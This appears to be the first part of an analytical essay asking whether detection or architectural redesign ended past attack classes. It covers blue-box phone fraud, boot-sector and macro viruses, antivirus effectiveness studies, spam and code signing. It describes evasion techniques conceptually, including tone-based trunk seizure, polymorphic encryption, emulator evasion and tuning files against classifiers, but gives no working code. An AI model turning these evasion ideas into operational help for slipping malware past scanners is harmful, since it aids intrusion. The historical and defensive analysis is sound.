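# Did Detection or Architectural Change End Past Classes of Computer Attack?

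## Instructions, data and what it means for a class of attack to end

A computer attack is an attempt to make a computer or network do something its owner does not want. Defenders can try to recognise hostile input and stop it, as an antivirus program does, or they can rebuild the system so that the same input has no effect. People who secure AI systems disagree about which approach to rely on, and those who favour rebuilding often appeal to history. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) look back at the classes of attack that engineers have managed to end and conclude that "detection lost and structure won".

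That claim concerns what happened to particular kinds of attack over several decades, so it can be checked. The oldest case in the debate comes from the telephone network, and it is simple enough to use for defining the terms.

### Forged tones on the telephone network

In the mid-twentieth century AT&T's Bell System, which ran most of the US telephone network, automated long-distance calling with audible tones. Exchanges sent each other instructions over the same circuits that carried the callers' voices, which is called in-band signalling. *Common Channel Interoffice Signaling* (Ritchie and Menard, 1978) describes the two sets of tones then in use. A single tone, on or off, showed whether a circuit was busy or free. Pairs of tones from a set of six carried the digits of the number and a few control signals.

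Anyone who could produce those tones could operate the network. *The great blue box phone frauds* (Flory, 1990) describes the method. The caller dialled a free or cheap number, such as directory assistance or an 800 number, to reach a trunk, which is a circuit between exchanges. The caller then played a 2,600 Hz tone from a "blue box", a small tone generator. Equipment at the far end of the trunk responded as if the call had finished and prepared for a new one, but the caller's own exchange had received no such signal and kept the line open. The caller then keyed in the tones for the number they really wanted, while the billing equipment still recorded the original call. Schneier (2024), in *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity*, recalls that John Draper found he could make the 2,600 Hz tone without a box, using a plastic whistle from a cereal packet.

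The telephone companies tried to find the people using blue boxes. Full Disclosure's *Death of the Blue Box* (1991) reprints testimony that company lawyers and an FBI agent gave to the National Wiretap Commission in the 1970s. Staff at the Central Telephone Company of Nevada read through printouts of calls to toll-free numbers and picked out implausible ones, such as a half-hour call to an airline's information desk. They then put a recorder on the suspect line. In about six months of 1973, the company gave the FBI about 32 numbers. Five cases ended in indictments, prosecutors declined seven others, and some searches found no device. The agent, Michael Simon, thought the method would be nearly impossible in a city of high-rise apartments, where agents could not reach the right door before the call ended. AT&T's lawyer estimated that the company had handled about a thousand cases of its own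 in ten years, and said that in most of them it had been less lucky than the Las Vegas investigators.

None of this fixed the flaw, but it did catch people who exploited it. In 1976 police arrested 160 users of toll-fraud devices, and courts convicted 144 of them. Bell Laboratories was still working on the problem in 1978, when Keys and Ratti filed a patent there for a way to identify fraudulent calls.

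By then the Bell System had already begun the other remedy. In May 1976 it linked an exchange in Madison, Wisconsin, to one in Chicago with a new system, Common Channel Interoffice Signaling (CCIS). The exchanges' processors sent each other instructions over a separate data link, and the voice circuits carried only voices, so nothing on the trunk responded when a caller whistled at 2,600 Hz. Schneier credits Signaling System 7 (SS7), the standard of the 1980s, with ending the fraud, but CCIS did the same thing earlier, and Flory calls it the permanent solution to the blue box.

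On the published evidence, fraud was a minor reason for the change. Ritchie and Menard list four limitations of the old tones. They were slow, so a call crossing several links could take 10 to 20 seconds to connect. They allowed too few signals for the new services the company wanted to sell. They were open to interference, and it is here that Ritchie and Menard mention fraud, in half a sentence. They also needed costly equipment at both ends of every voice channel. Engineers had known about these limitations for years, but the push for change came in the early 1960s from computer-controlled exchanges, which needed a faster way to communicate.

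The idea went back to at least 1922, when a separate signalling circuit went on trial between New York and Philadelphia, according to a history in the same journal issue as Ritchie and Menard. Flory reports that the industry rejected the method in the 1950s as too costly and too difficult. The company may have had its own reasons to keep quiet about fraud in its journal, and a thousand cases is a substantial number. Still, Bell's engineers justified the change in print on grounds of speed, capacity and cost, and the end of the blue box looks largely like a by-product. Narisetty and colleagues use the telephone as an analogy and say outright that they are making no claim about why SS7 came about. Those who cite the telephone as a victory for architecture are right that the redesign worked, but the example gives them less evidence that a company will pay for such a redesign when security is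 the only return.

### Terms

A *vulnerability* is a flaw an attacker could use, and an *exploit* is the input or program that uses it. In the telephone network, the vulnerability was the shared circuit and the exploit was a sequence of tones. An *attack class* includes all attacks that exploit the same underlying flaw, regardless of the program attacked or the exact input. Draper's whistle and the home-made box that a woman in Las Vegas used to phone her mother in Miami therefore belong to the same class.

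The flaw behind the blue box was *instruction-data confusion*, in which a system treats data as an instruction. The caller's sound was data, but the exchange treated it as an instruction. Schneier traces buffer overflows and SQL injection, two attacks on ordinary software, to the same flaw, as does David C's 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. Boot-sector viruses, discussed below, fit the description more loosely.

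*Detection* means judging whether a given input, file or action is hostile, and blocking it if so. The judgement may rest on a *signature*, a stored pattern taken from a known attack, or on a *classifier*, a trained model that scores how likely an input is to be hostile. In Las Vegas, a clerk made the judgement using a printout. An *architectural defence* is a change in the design of a system that limits what input can do, without judging whether the input is hostile. CCIS, for example, did not try to distinguish hostile whistles from innocent ones. As Schneier notes, AT&T also had the option of changing the tones or trying to keep them secret, but that only forces the attacker to write a new exploit.

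Architectural defences come in several forms. *Separation* keeps instructions and data apart so that the system never executes data, as in CCIS. *Blocking automatic execution* means that the system runs incoming material only when someone asks it to. For example, a PC that starts only from its own hard disk ignores any floppy disk left in the drive. *Containment* accepts that an attacker may take over a component and limits what that component can then do. AT&T would have been using containment if it had kept the tones but barred trunks reached through 800 numbers from dialling overseas, so that blue boxes still worked but only for shorter distances.

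A *language model agent* is a language model that can use tools to take actions, such as sending mail, running code or making payments. *Prompt injection* is an attack in which text planted in what a language model reads makes the model follow the attacker's instructions.

### Four meanings of "ended"

When somebody writes that a class of attack is over, the word can carry any of four meanings.

1. Nobody can write the flaw any more, because the tools or the equipment leave no way to make the mistake.
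2. The flaw still exists, but attackers cannot exploit it, because something else in the system stands in the way.
3. Attackers can still exploit the flaw, but they rarely do.
4. Attackers have moved to something else.

These kinds of ending do not come in a fixed order, and more than one can hold at once. They also differ a good deal in how much they help the defender. If nobody can write the flaw, the protection lasts as long as the design does. If the attack has only become rare, it may stay rare only until someone finds a reason to try it again. If attackers switch to another method when one is closed off, the victims may be no better off. This is the problem of *displacement*, and it means that use of the old method falls more than total harm does.

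The flaw that blue boxes exploited was completely gone on routes that used CCIS at every step, because no equipment on the voice circuit responded to tones. But the Bell System converted its exchanges one at a time. Ritchie and Menard expected CCIS to cover about 80 percent of the trunks between long-distance exchanges by 1985, nine years after the first link. In the meantime, plenty of old exchanges still responded to 2,600 Hz, but a blue box could work from end to end only where every exchange along the route was of the old type. A growing number of callers therefore could not exploit the flaw, even though it still existed in the old exchanges.

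According to Telephone World's *Wawina, MN Telephone Sounds*, the last trunks in the continental United States to use the tones served Wawina, Minnesota, whose telephone company had fewer than 40 customers. The company replaced them on June 15, 2006, thirty years after the change in Madison and Chicago. For much of that time, blue-box fraud was possible but rare.

Some attackers moved to other methods. Red boxes, which imitate the tones a pay phone makes when someone drops in a coin, spread in the 1990s, after the blue box had stopped being much use. The separate channel has had security problems too. Schneier (2024), in *Entries Tagged "phones"*, reports that the Federal Communications Commission, the US telecoms regulator, asked carriers in March 2024 what they were doing about vulnerabilities in SS7 that allow surveillance. By the definition above, this is a different class of attack,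 because nobody gets into SS7 by playing tones down a telephone. The separation held and the original class of attack ended, but the telephone network went on having security problems, which accounts of the blue box that stop in the 1980s tend to leave out.

Boot-sector viruses ended differently. The boot sector is the first sector of a disk, and on a disk that can start a computer, it holds a short program that the computer runs before anything else. PCs of the 1980s and early 1990s commonly tried the floppy drive first. If someone had left a floppy in the drive, the PC ran whatever was in its boot sector at the next startup, including a virus. The virus then copied itself to the hard disk, stayed in memory and wrote itself to other floppies as people used them. The PC was running a program from a disk that its owner thought of as a container for files.

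For years these were the most common viruses in circulation. *Computer Viruses* (White, Kephart and Chess, 1995) found that they made up the overwhelming majority of incidents, and predicted that new operating systems such as Windows 95 and the spread of networks would change this. In the yearly rankings in Virus Bulletin's *Throwback Thursday* (2000), Form, a boot-sector virus, led in 1995 with 328 reported incidents, or 13.3 percent of the total. The next year Concept took first place. It was a macro virus, a type that travels inside documents, and macro viruses held first place for four years.

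Windows 95 might deserve some of the credit, since it changed how programs reached the disk. According to an account from the publisher O'Reilly, its 32-bit driver stopped most viruses from writing to the boot sector of a floppy. But in the tests reported in *Windows 95 and Viruses*, every virus loaded itself into memory, and most of them could still infect floppies. A disk setting probably explains the disagreement. *Computer Viruses on New Operating Systems* describes trials in which most boot-sector viruses kept spreading if the user had selected the older, 16-bit form of disk access. Windows 95 also included a form of detection, a warning that the boot record had changed. In the *Windows 95 and Viruses* tests, the warning appeared only at the first restart after an infection, and never for two of the viruses, Michelangelo and Telefonica.

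The architectural change worked on some machines, and the detector missed some viruses. Commercial antivirus programs were removing infections throughout and probably made some difference. But boot-sector viruses could have faded without any of these defenses, because they spread when people exchanged floppy disks, and people were starting to send files by e-mail instead. Later PCs had no floppy drive. This decline didn't require making the boot sector safe, and PCs were still running code from whatever disk was in the machine after most of the viruses that relied on this had disappeared.

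Of the four meanings, the first never applied to boot-sector viruses and the second applied only in part. The viruses did become rare, and later virus writers moved to documents and e-mail. But this decline is weak evidence for any defence, whether detection or architectural change, because the floppy disks that carried the viruses were disappearing over the same years. Attacks that used databases, documents or programs written in memory-unsafe languages are better test cases, because all of these stayed in heavy use.

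### What the counts measure

Most arguments about whether a class of attack has ended rely on one of a few public counts, each of which measures something narrower than people use it to show.

Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE) is a public list that gives each disclosed flaw its own number. Each record stands for one flaw in one product or a group of related products, and does not show that anyone has used the flaw in an attack. The list leaves out flaws that nobody has found or that the finder kept private, and it covers widely installed software far better than the code behind a single company's website. The total also rises when more people search for flaws or more organisations report them, even if programmers are making no more mistakes.

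The Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE) classifies flaws by type and has more than 900 entries. MITRE, the US non-profit that maintains it, ranks the types every year. Its 2025 list, *CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses*, draws on 39,080 CVE records and is meant to show which weaknesses are most common and severe. It is the closest thing to a ranking of attack classes, and people cite it as one.

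A weakness can move in that table for reasons unrelated to software. Up to 2024, MITRE folded the labels on CVE records into a simplified set of 130 types before counting. In 2025 it counted the labels as the reporting organisations had supplied them. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Key Insights* (2025) reports that CWE-269, which covers faulty management of privileges, had 219 records under the new method and would have had 633 if MITRE had folded in its subtypes. CWE-269 fell off the list, and MITRE thinks the old method would probably have kept it on. Over the same year, the share of records with a type supplied by the organisation publishing them rose from 53 to 67 percent. A reader who compared the 2024 and 2025 rankings without knowing about these changes could easily mistake a change in labelling for a decline in a class of weakness.

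The Known Exploited Vulnerabilities catalogue, or KEV, comes closer to recording real attacks. The US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency started it in 2021 and adds a flaw when it has a CVE number, reliable evidence that someone has exploited it, and a remedy that users can apply. These criteria exclude the thousands of flaws that no attacker ever exploited, but also attacks that no one noticed and attacks on flaws without a CVE number. Each flaw gets one entry, whether a spy agency used it against one ministry or criminals used it against a hundred thousand firms. Because the catalogue is so recent, it contains little evidence about attacks that peaked in the 1990s or 2000s.

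The main source for those years is infection telemetry, meaning reports of malicious software from the machines or organisations that met it. Martin (2016), in *Throwback Thursday*, describes a long-running example, the monthly table of reported incidents of each virus that the trade journal Virus Bulletin kept from 1992 to 2013. Such tables correct the common mistake of judging the danger from viruses by the number known. *How Prevalent are Computer Viruses?*, from the early 1990s, points out that people had written hundreds of PC viruses but only a small minority were spreading. Counting CVE records to judge danger has the same weakness.

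Telemetry has its own problems. An antivirus program cannot report what it fails to recognise, so the count is most complete for attacks that detection already handles. Telemetry can also mix up attempted infections with successful ones. NCSA (1997), a survey by the US National Computer Security Association, has separate tables for virus encounters and infections, but not every source separates them, and a virus that a scanner blocks a thousand times can look like an epidemic. A single outlier can also distort a year's figures. In Virus Bulletin's 2000 list, the macro virus ColdApe accounts for 8,622 incidents in 1999, a quarter of all those reported, while the previous year's leader had 953. Who pays for the figures also matters. A contributor to Virus Bulletin's *Throwback Thursday* (1993) complained that antivirus companies' marketing had obscured the true extent of the problem with projections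 and speculation.

All these measures can mislead because a class's share of reported flaws, its total count and its rate for a given amount of software can move in different directions. Suppose 1,000 of the 10,000 flaws reported in one year belong to one class, and ten years later 2,000 of 40,000 do. The class's share has fallen from 10 percent to 5 percent, but its count has doubled. If there is also ten times as much software, an amount that once had 1,000 of these reported flaws now has 200, a fall of four-fifths.

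| | First year | Ten years later |
|---|---|---|
| All reported flaws | 10,000 | 40,000 |
| Flaws in the class | 1,000 | 2,000 |
| Share of all flaws | 10% | 5% |
| Amount of software (first year = 1) | 1 | 10 |
| Flaws in the class per unit of software | 1,000 | 200 |

All of these figures are correct, but they are useful for different things. The last row helps show whether programmers have learned to avoid the mistake, while the count matters to an administrator with patches to install. The share is mostly useful for deciding which problem to work on next, yet it is the figure people cite most often when they claim that a class is dying. The differences between these measures partly explain how David C can call SQL injection "now rarely seen in websites" in the same month that MITRE reported almost 1,000 more records of it than the year before.

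Virus infections from floppy disks seem to have still been rising when e-mail overtook floppies as the leading source. ZDNet's *Study* (1999) reports a survey in which floppies accounted for two-thirds of infections in 1998 and 39 percent in 1999, the year e-mail passed them. The same survey found 32 infections a month for every 1,000 computers in 1998 and 88 in February 1999. Infections of all kinds had risen about fourfold in two years. Multiplying the rates by the shares gives roughly 21 floppy infections a month per 1,000 computers in 1998 and 34 in 1999. This estimate is rough because it applies a yearly share to a monthly rate, and because floppies carried infected documents as well as boot-sector viruses.

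## Signature detection and the persistence of malware

The standard defence against these viruses was the antivirus scanner, about as pure an example of detection as exists. Scanners have not eliminated malware, the general name for malicious programs, in around forty years of use. We can infer little from this about how many infections they prevented, and the field studies that tried to measure that number disagree with one another.

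### How a scanner recognises a program

The simplest kind of signature is a sequence of bytes that occurs in every copy of a virus and, ideally, in no legitimate program. An analyst picks the sequence from a captured copy, and the scanner searches each file for it. Fred Cohen's *Computer Viruses: Theory and Experiments* (1987) describes a toy version. The example virus puts 1234567 on the first line of every program it infects, so that it does not infect the same program twice. The scanner reads the first line of each program before running it and refuses to run it if the number is there. This detects every copy of the virus until someone who knows about the scanner changes the number to 123456.

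Scanners also use hashes, which are short fingerprints calculated from a whole file. The scanner looks up a file's hash in a list of hashes of known malware. The lookup is fast and almost never confuses two files. But changing any byte of the file produces a completely different hash, whereas a byte pattern still matches after changes to the rest of the file.

Polymorphic viruses exploit this weakness by changing their own code each time they copy themselves. Cohen's example inserts random, useless statements between the functional ones. More commonly, the virus encrypts most of itself with a new key for each copy, leaving only a short decryption routine unencrypted. It also rewrites that routine by reordering instructions or adding ones that have no effect. Every copy does the same thing, but the copies may share no sequence of bytes that could serve as a signature.

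Antivirus companies responded with heuristic rules, emulation and trained classifiers. Heuristic rules look for features that are common in malware and rare elsewhere, such as a program that decrypts itself and then opens other programs to modify them. Emulation runs the start of a suspect program inside a simulated computer, where it can do no harm. An encrypted virus has to decrypt itself before it can work, and the scanner can then search the simulated memory for an ordinary signature. Virus writers responded with programs that run useless instructions until the emulator stops, or that check for signs of a simulation and do nothing harmful if they find them. Trained classifiers learn which features to look for from large collections of malicious and clean files. They can flag a file that no analyst has seen, but an attacker with a copy of the classifier can keep altering a file until it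 is no longer flagged.

By the early 2010s, commercial products also blocked dangerous web addresses, monitored what programs did, and checked files against online databases updated by millions of other installations. Signatures remained useful. AV-Comparatives' *Real-World Protection Test March-June 2013* (2013) points out that an updated signature can find malware that the scanner missed the first time, for example on a company's file server, while the newer methods often cannot check files already there.

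### Cohen's proof

Cohen also proved that no scanner can be perfect. The short proof appears in *Cure of Computer Viruses* (1984) and in the 1987 paper. Cohen calls a program a virus if it can infect others, which means changing them so that they contain a copy of it, whether exact or altered.

1. Suppose someone has written a perfect detector, D. Given any program, D always finishes and always answers correctly whether the program is a virus.
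2. D is itself a program, so another program can contain a copy of D and run it.
3. Write a program, C, that runs D on C's own code. If D answers "virus", C infects nothing. If D answers "not a virus", C infects another program.
4. If D calls C a virus, C never infects anything. C is therefore not a virus, and D is wrong.
5. If D calls C clean, C goes on to infect another program. C is therefore a virus, and D is wrong again.
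6. D gives a wrong answer about C either way, so a perfect detector cannot exist.

Cohen uses the same trick to show that no program can always determine whether two mutated copies of a virus are equivalent. He builds two variants that each run the detector on the pair. If it reports that they are equivalent, one prints 1 and the other prints 0; otherwise they behave identically, so the detector is wrong either way.

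Detecting viruses by watching what programs do has the same problem as detecting them by reading code. Cohen's example is a compiler, which turns a programmer's text into a working program. A compiler that compiles a new version of itself fits his definition of a virus, although it is working as intended. Whether a given use of the compiler is an attack depends on its input text, and Cohen had just shown that judging that text perfectly is impossible.

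For each detector, the proof correctly constructs one program that the detector gets wrong. It doesn't show that the detector gets many programs wrong, or any that people actually encounter, though it is sometimes read that way. The defender can also choose which error the detector makes on the constructed program. If D calls C a virus, C does nothing, so the only harm is a false alarm about a program that nobody needs. Cohen suggests accepting some false alarms and some missed viruses to catch a large number of viruses. He adds that an attacker who knows the detector's threshold can stay just below it, though he thinks the defender could still keep the infection slow.

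The paper whose proof is cited in favour of architecture also finds difficulties with architectural defences. Cohen finds that a system can prevent viruses from spreading only if it restricts the sharing of information, restricts how far shared information can travel, or gives up the general ability to treat data as a program. Tracking the flow of information exactly would take too much computation. Simpler approximations err on the side of caution, and over time they block more and more legitimate sharing. He concludes that the only provably safe policy at the time was isolation, which he calls unacceptable for anyone who wants to benefit from other people's work.

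In July 1984 he also tried a virus on a system with an architectural defence, a Univac 1108 that used the Bell-LaPadula model to stop secrets from flowing from a higher security level to a lower one. He had two weeks on the machine, and after 26 hours of computer time his virus could spread from one user to another and from a lower security level to a higher one. The model's rules allowed upward movement, so the virus could spread this way without exploiting a mistake in the implementation.

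### Why false alarms limit a scanner

A scanner that makes few mistakes can still produce mostly false alarms, because hostile files are rare. Suppose that 1 file in 10,000 is hostile, and that a scanner catches 99 percent of hostile files and wrongly flags 1 percent of clean ones. Out of a million files, 100 are hostile and the scanner catches 99 of them. It also flags 1 percent of the 999,900 clean files, which is 9,999. The share of its alarms that are real is

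99 ÷ (99 + 9,999) ≈ 0.98 percent.

About 99 in every 100 alarms are false. Catching more malware hardly changes this, because even if the scanner caught all 100 hostile files, only 0.99 percent of its alarms would be correct. Flagging fewer clean files helps much more, and so does scanning material in which attacks are common.

| Share of items that are hostile | Share of clean items wrongly flagged | Share of alarms that are real |
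|---|---|---|
| 1 in 10,000 | 1% | about 1% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 0.01% | about 50% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 0.0001% | about 99% |
| 1 in 2 | 1% | 99% |

Commercial scanners have to operate near the third row, because users will not tolerate a program that keeps deleting their files. A post on the blog Secure Hunter (2014), apparently from Microsoft's antimalware team, puts the impact of wrong detections at about one in a million in a normal month. In one month it rose to one in 100,000, after someone built a clean file to trick antivirus companies into flagging it. It is unclear from the post whether the figure counts computers or files. If it counts computers, the rate per file is lower still, since each computer holds many thousands of files. The 1 percent in the example is therefore far too pessimistic for antivirus, though it may suit a new classifier that has not had years of tuning. To keep false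 alarms this rare, a scanner has to let through files that are merely suspicious.

### Whether antivirus prevents infections

Laboratory tests can't establish how well this compromise works, because the tester chooses the malware and no real user is involved. Lalonde Lévesque, Nsiempba and colleagues (2013), in *A Clinical Study of Risk Factors Related to Malware Infections*, borrowed the method of medical trials. They sold discounted laptops to 50 people recruited on a Montreal university campus and followed the buyers for four months in 2011 and 2012. Every laptop ran Windows 7 and an antivirus product from Trend Micro. Participants used the laptops as their own and brought them in once a month for the researchers to check with other diagnostic tools.

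The antivirus program caught 95 different threats on 19 of the laptops, or 38 percent. One user accounted for 28 of them. The monthly checks found that ten laptops, or 20 percent, had unwanted software that the antivirus program had missed. Most of it was adware and browser toolbars. The clearest case of malware was a fake antivirus program that kept closing the user's other applications and asking for payment details.

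*Technological and Human Factors of Malware Attacks* (Lalonde Lévesque, Chiasson and colleagues, 2018) reports a reanalysis in which Trend Micro's antivirus product caught 95 of 115 threats, or 83 percent. Leaving out 12 missed items that were only "unwanted software" raises the figure to 92 percent. Two commercial laboratories had given the company's product 98 and 99 percent for the same period. A rescan of 19 of the missed files several months later still flagged none of them. Trend Micro may not have considered them hostile. If so, part of the gap between 83 and 99 percent comes from disagreement over what counts as malware, which better scanning would not remove.

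The trial tested only one antivirus product, whose maker partly funded the study, and it had no group without antivirus. The 2013 paper infers that at least 38 percent of users would have been infected without protection, but this assumes that every file the scanner stopped would otherwise have run and infected the computer, and nobody knows how many would have.

Microsoft has data on both groups from far more computers. *Microsoft Security Intelligence Report, Volume 14* (Alyias, Batchelder and colleagues, 2013) used reports from the Malicious Software Removal Tool, which most Windows computers download and run every month. In the second half of 2012, about 24 percent of the computers had no up-to-date antivirus program running. Each month, the tool removed malware from 11.6 to 13.6 of every 1,000 of these unprotected computers, compared with 1.4 to 3.8 of every 1,000 protected ones. On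 average, infection was 5.5 times as common on the unprotected computers. Microsoft announced this result in *Malware Infections 5.5 Times More Likely Without Antivirus Software* (2013). A later Microsoft analysis put the ratio at 7.1 for computers that never had protection compared with those that always did.

These ratios would measure the benefit of antivirus only if the two groups of users were otherwise alike, and they weren't. Alyias and colleagues list several reasons why a computer might be unprotected, and two of them could produce much of the gap even if antivirus had no effect. Some malware switches off antivirus programs, so the infection causes the lack of protection. Some users turn the scanner off to run programs that it would block, and these people are likely to pick up more malware anyway. The removal tool also looks only for selected common families of malware, which antivirus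 products should be best at recognising, so a protected computer infected only with rarer malware counts as clean.

The version of Windows also made a large difference. Among unprotected computers, the tool cleaned 15.6 in every 1,000 running Windows XP and 2.7 in every 1,000 running the 32-bit edition of Windows 8. The rate for XP with antivirus was 4.2, higher than for Windows 8 without it. Windows 8 had been on sale for only about two months, and new computers have had less time to collect infections, but the gap is still wide. In the first half of 2013, according to Microsoft (2013), the supported versions of Windows encountered malware at roughly similar rates, between 12 and 20 percent of computers, yet infections were six times as common on XP as on Windows 8. That difference is partly due to changes in how Microsoft built Windows and partly due to detection, since Windows 8 was the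 first version to include antivirus by default.

Expired antivirus programs offer a better comparison. Many come with a new computer as a free trial that the owner never renews. SC Magazine's *Microsoft report explores dangers of running expired security software* gives infection rates for home and other unmanaged computers running Windows 8 and 8.1: 0.6 percent with up-to-date protection, 2.2 percent with expired protection and 2.4 percent with none. Computers with expired protection were infected almost as often as those with none, as one would expect if current signatures prevented many infections. People who let a subscription lapse may also be careless in other ways, so this comparison doesn't remove the problem, but it makes it harder to believe that the whole benefit comes from the kind of person who installs antivirus.

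Other comparisons found a much smaller gap, or one in the opposite direction. Lalonde Lévesque and colleagues report that in 2009 the security company SurfRight scanned 107,435 users' computers and found infections on 32 percent of those with up-to-date antivirus and 46 percent of those without. People who seek out an extra scanner often suspect that something is wrong, which pushes up both figures. In *Measuring Security Practices and How They Impact Security*, DeKoven, Randall and colleagues (2019) monitored network traffic from 15,291 computers in student residences at the University of California, San Diego, for six months. Among Windows computers, 7 percent of those with antivirus were compromised, compared with 4 percent of those without.

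Antivirus programs are unlikely to have caused those infections. DeKoven and colleagues point out that they mostly counted malware that antivirus had failed to catch, which leaves out its successes. They also found that 12 percent of Windows computers with a password manager were compromised, compared with 7 percent of those without one, although password managers are unlikely to cause infections. In the Montreal trial, seven of the nine participants with the most computer expertise encountered malware, compared with 16 of the other 41. Differences between users can evidently be large enough to hide or exaggerate the software's effect. Antivirus probably prevents many infections with common malware, but the figure of 5.5 is more likely to overstate its effect than to understate it.

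### Half a million files a day

A great deal of malware is in circulation. Kaspersky's *The number of the year* (2025) reports that the company's systems detected an average of 500,000 malicious files a day in 2025, 7 percent more than the year before, and that 48 percent of Windows users were targets of some kind of threat. *Malware*, a web page from the German testing institute AV-TEST, reports over 450,000 new malicious or unwanted programs a day, but the page gave the same number in April 2022, so the figure can't be used to measure recent growth.

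These figures count distinct files, which attackers can produce easily through polymorphism. If an attacker's server repackages the same program for each of a thousand victims, the count goes up by a thousand. AV-TEST notes that many samples are active only for a short time. Much of the total therefore reflects attackers' efforts to get past signatures, and it would probably be far lower if nobody used scanners. Like the number of known viruses in the early 1990s, it does not measure harm.

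Infection rates are more informative but can also jump for odd reasons. The rate Microsoft reported rose from 5.6 to 17.8 per 1,000 computers in the last quarter of 2013, according to BetaNews in *Windows 7 shows higher infection rates than XP in last quarter of 2013* (2014). Most of the increase came from Rotbrow, a program presented as protection against unwanted browser add-ons.

Current security products do very well in laboratory tests. In AVLab's *Recent Results in January 2026* (2026), 12 products blocked an average of 100 percent of 334 malware samples. Yet criminals were still using malware to steal data and sell it. Kaspersky (2026) analysed five million log files from password-stealing malware that appeared on the dark web in 2025. In about 35 percent of cases, the malicious file had been in the Windows temporary files folder, which suggests that the victim had downloaded it and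 run it straight away. The files often posed as installers, game modifications or tools for activating pirated software, and many victims had followed the attacker's instructions to turn off their antivirus program before running them.

A scanner cannot help once its owner has turned it off. These cases also show why "malware" is a poor candidate for an attack class that could end. The victims' computers had no particular flaw and were doing what general-purpose computers are for, which is running the programs their owners choose. Self-copying viruses, the first problem scanners had to deal with, have become a smaller share of malware. AV-TEST's *Heightened threat scenario*, a summary of its 2018/2019 security report, puts classic viruses at 21 percent and worms at 7 percent. Trojans, which pose as something useful and rely on the user to start them, were by far the most popular choice for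 attacks on Windows.

### Spam

Detection has done better against email spam. Mail providers have relied on trained filters since the early 2000s, and spammers have never stopped sending. AV-TEST reported in October 2026 that nearly half of the 390 billion emails sent every day were spam, but spam makes up a smaller share of an ordinary inbox. Email would not still be usable if people had to sort through the spam themselves.

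Spam is unusually well suited to detection. Because nearly half of all mail is spam, a filter with the error rates in the example above would be right about 99 percent of the messages it flagged. Mistakes also do little harm. A missed advertisement wastes a few seconds of the reader's time, and a legitimate message flagged by mistake usually waits in a junk folder. Large providers see the same message arrive at thousands of accounts, and their users supply new training data whenever they mark something as junk.

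Spammers also need volume. If a filter stops 99 messages in 100, the sender has to send a hundred times as many to reach the same number of people. That can ruin a business that earns a fraction of a cent per message, but it does much less to stop an attacker who needs to succeed only once. If each of 100 attempts has an independent 1 percent chance of getting past the filter, the chance that at least one succeeds is 63 percent. An *adaptive attacker*, who knows the defence and designs the attack against it, can improve those odds by testing messages in advance. AV-TEST estimates that 3 to 5 percent of spam is phishing, which tries to trick people into giving away passwords or money, and one reply may be enough to pay for the campaign. Web application firewalls, which screen requests to websites, and classifiers for prompt injection also face attackers who need only one success.

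Filters are only part of the reason less spam reaches people's inboxes. Mail systems now commonly check whether a server has permission to send mail for the domain it names, and whether a message carries that domain's digital signature. These checks make forgery harder without analyzing the message's content. But a spammer can register a domain and authenticate it properly, so messages that pass the checks still need to be filtered.

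### Running only approved programs

A scanner blocks programs that it recognises as hostile and lets the rest run. With allowlisting, the computer instead runs only programs on an approved list. Polymorphism then does not help the attacker, because an altered file is not on the list.

Code signing makes such a list practical. The publisher calculates a hash of the program and signs it with a private cryptographic key, and the user's computer checks the signature with the matching public key. If anyone has changed a byte, the check fails. On most PCs, a missing signature produces only a warning that the user can dismiss. Apple is much stricter with the iPhone. Since the App Store opened in 2008, iPhones have run only apps that Apple has approved, with limited exceptions. Ordinary criminal malware has been much rarer on iPhones than on Windows PCs, but Apple's approval process doesn't explain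 the whole difference, because iPhones also confine each app to its own area of the system.

Malware has still got past code signing. A signature shows which key signed a program and that nobody has altered the program since, but not that the program is safe or that the right person held the key. Stuxnet, the worm discovered in 2010 that sabotaged Iranian uranium centrifuges, installed drivers signed with keys stolen from two Taiwanese hardware companies. In 2015, Chinese developers downloaded altered copies of Xcode, Apple's programming tool, which added malicious code to the apps they built. The developers signed those apps in good faith, and Apple approved them. Researchers had known about this kind of attack since at least 1987, when Cohen's paper described a doctored compiler that inserted a backdoor whenever it compiled a system's login program.

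An approved program can also run unapproved instructions. Cohen noted that an interpreter, a program that carries out instructions written in a language such as BASIC, can remain unchanged while a virus spreads among the programs it runs. Macro viruses ran inside Microsoft Word, which is signed and appears on almost every company's list of approved programs. In about 32 percent of the cases Kaspersky studied, the malicious file was in a folder belonging to Microsoft's .NET software, a location Kaspersky associates with malware that hides inside legitimate processes.

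App stores also depend on detection. Apple and Google use human reviewers and automated scanning to decide which apps to approve. The restriction that stops a phone from running unapproved apps is architectural, but approving an app requires a judgement about whether it is hostile. Making that judgement in one place has advantages. A reviewer can spend hours on an app that a scanner on the device would have to clear in a fraction of a second. Developers need an account, which the store can close, and the store can withdraw an app it approved by mistake. An attacker also can't avoid the check by persuading the user to turn it off, as Kaspersky's victims did.

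The drawback is that owners can no longer run whatever they like. Cohen thought that almost any system useful for science or software development would need the general ability to run new programs, and most PCs still have it.

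## Macro viruses, AutoRun worms and the blocking of automatic execution

Blocking automatic execution is a milder change than allowing only approved programs, because owners can still run whatever they choose. Microsoft blocked it in Windows in 2011 for programs on USB drives, and in Office in 2022 for programs inside documents. Attacks that relied on each feature fell steeply, but the evidence that Microsoft's change caused the fall is much stronger for USB drives than for documents.

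### Programs inside documents

Word and Excel files can contain macros, small programs that automate repetitive work such as filling in a form or reformatting a table. A macro can also change other files, send mail and start other programs. Word runs some macros automatically. For example, it can run a macro named AutoOpen as soon as someone opens the document containing it. Word's designers intended the program to treat part of a document as instructions, although readers think of the file as text.

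Check Point Research's *The Death of “Please Enable Macros” and What it Means* (2022) traces the idea of a document virus to Joel McNamara, who wrote one as a demonstration in 1994 and kept it to himself. In 1995 an unknown author released Concept. When someone opened an infected document, Concept copied itself into Word's global template, a file whose macros are available in every document. It also took over the Save As command, so that documents the user later saved also carried the virus. Concept did little except show a strange dialogue box, and its code contained the remark "that's enough to prove my point". By late 1997 it reportedly accounted for half of all virus infections.

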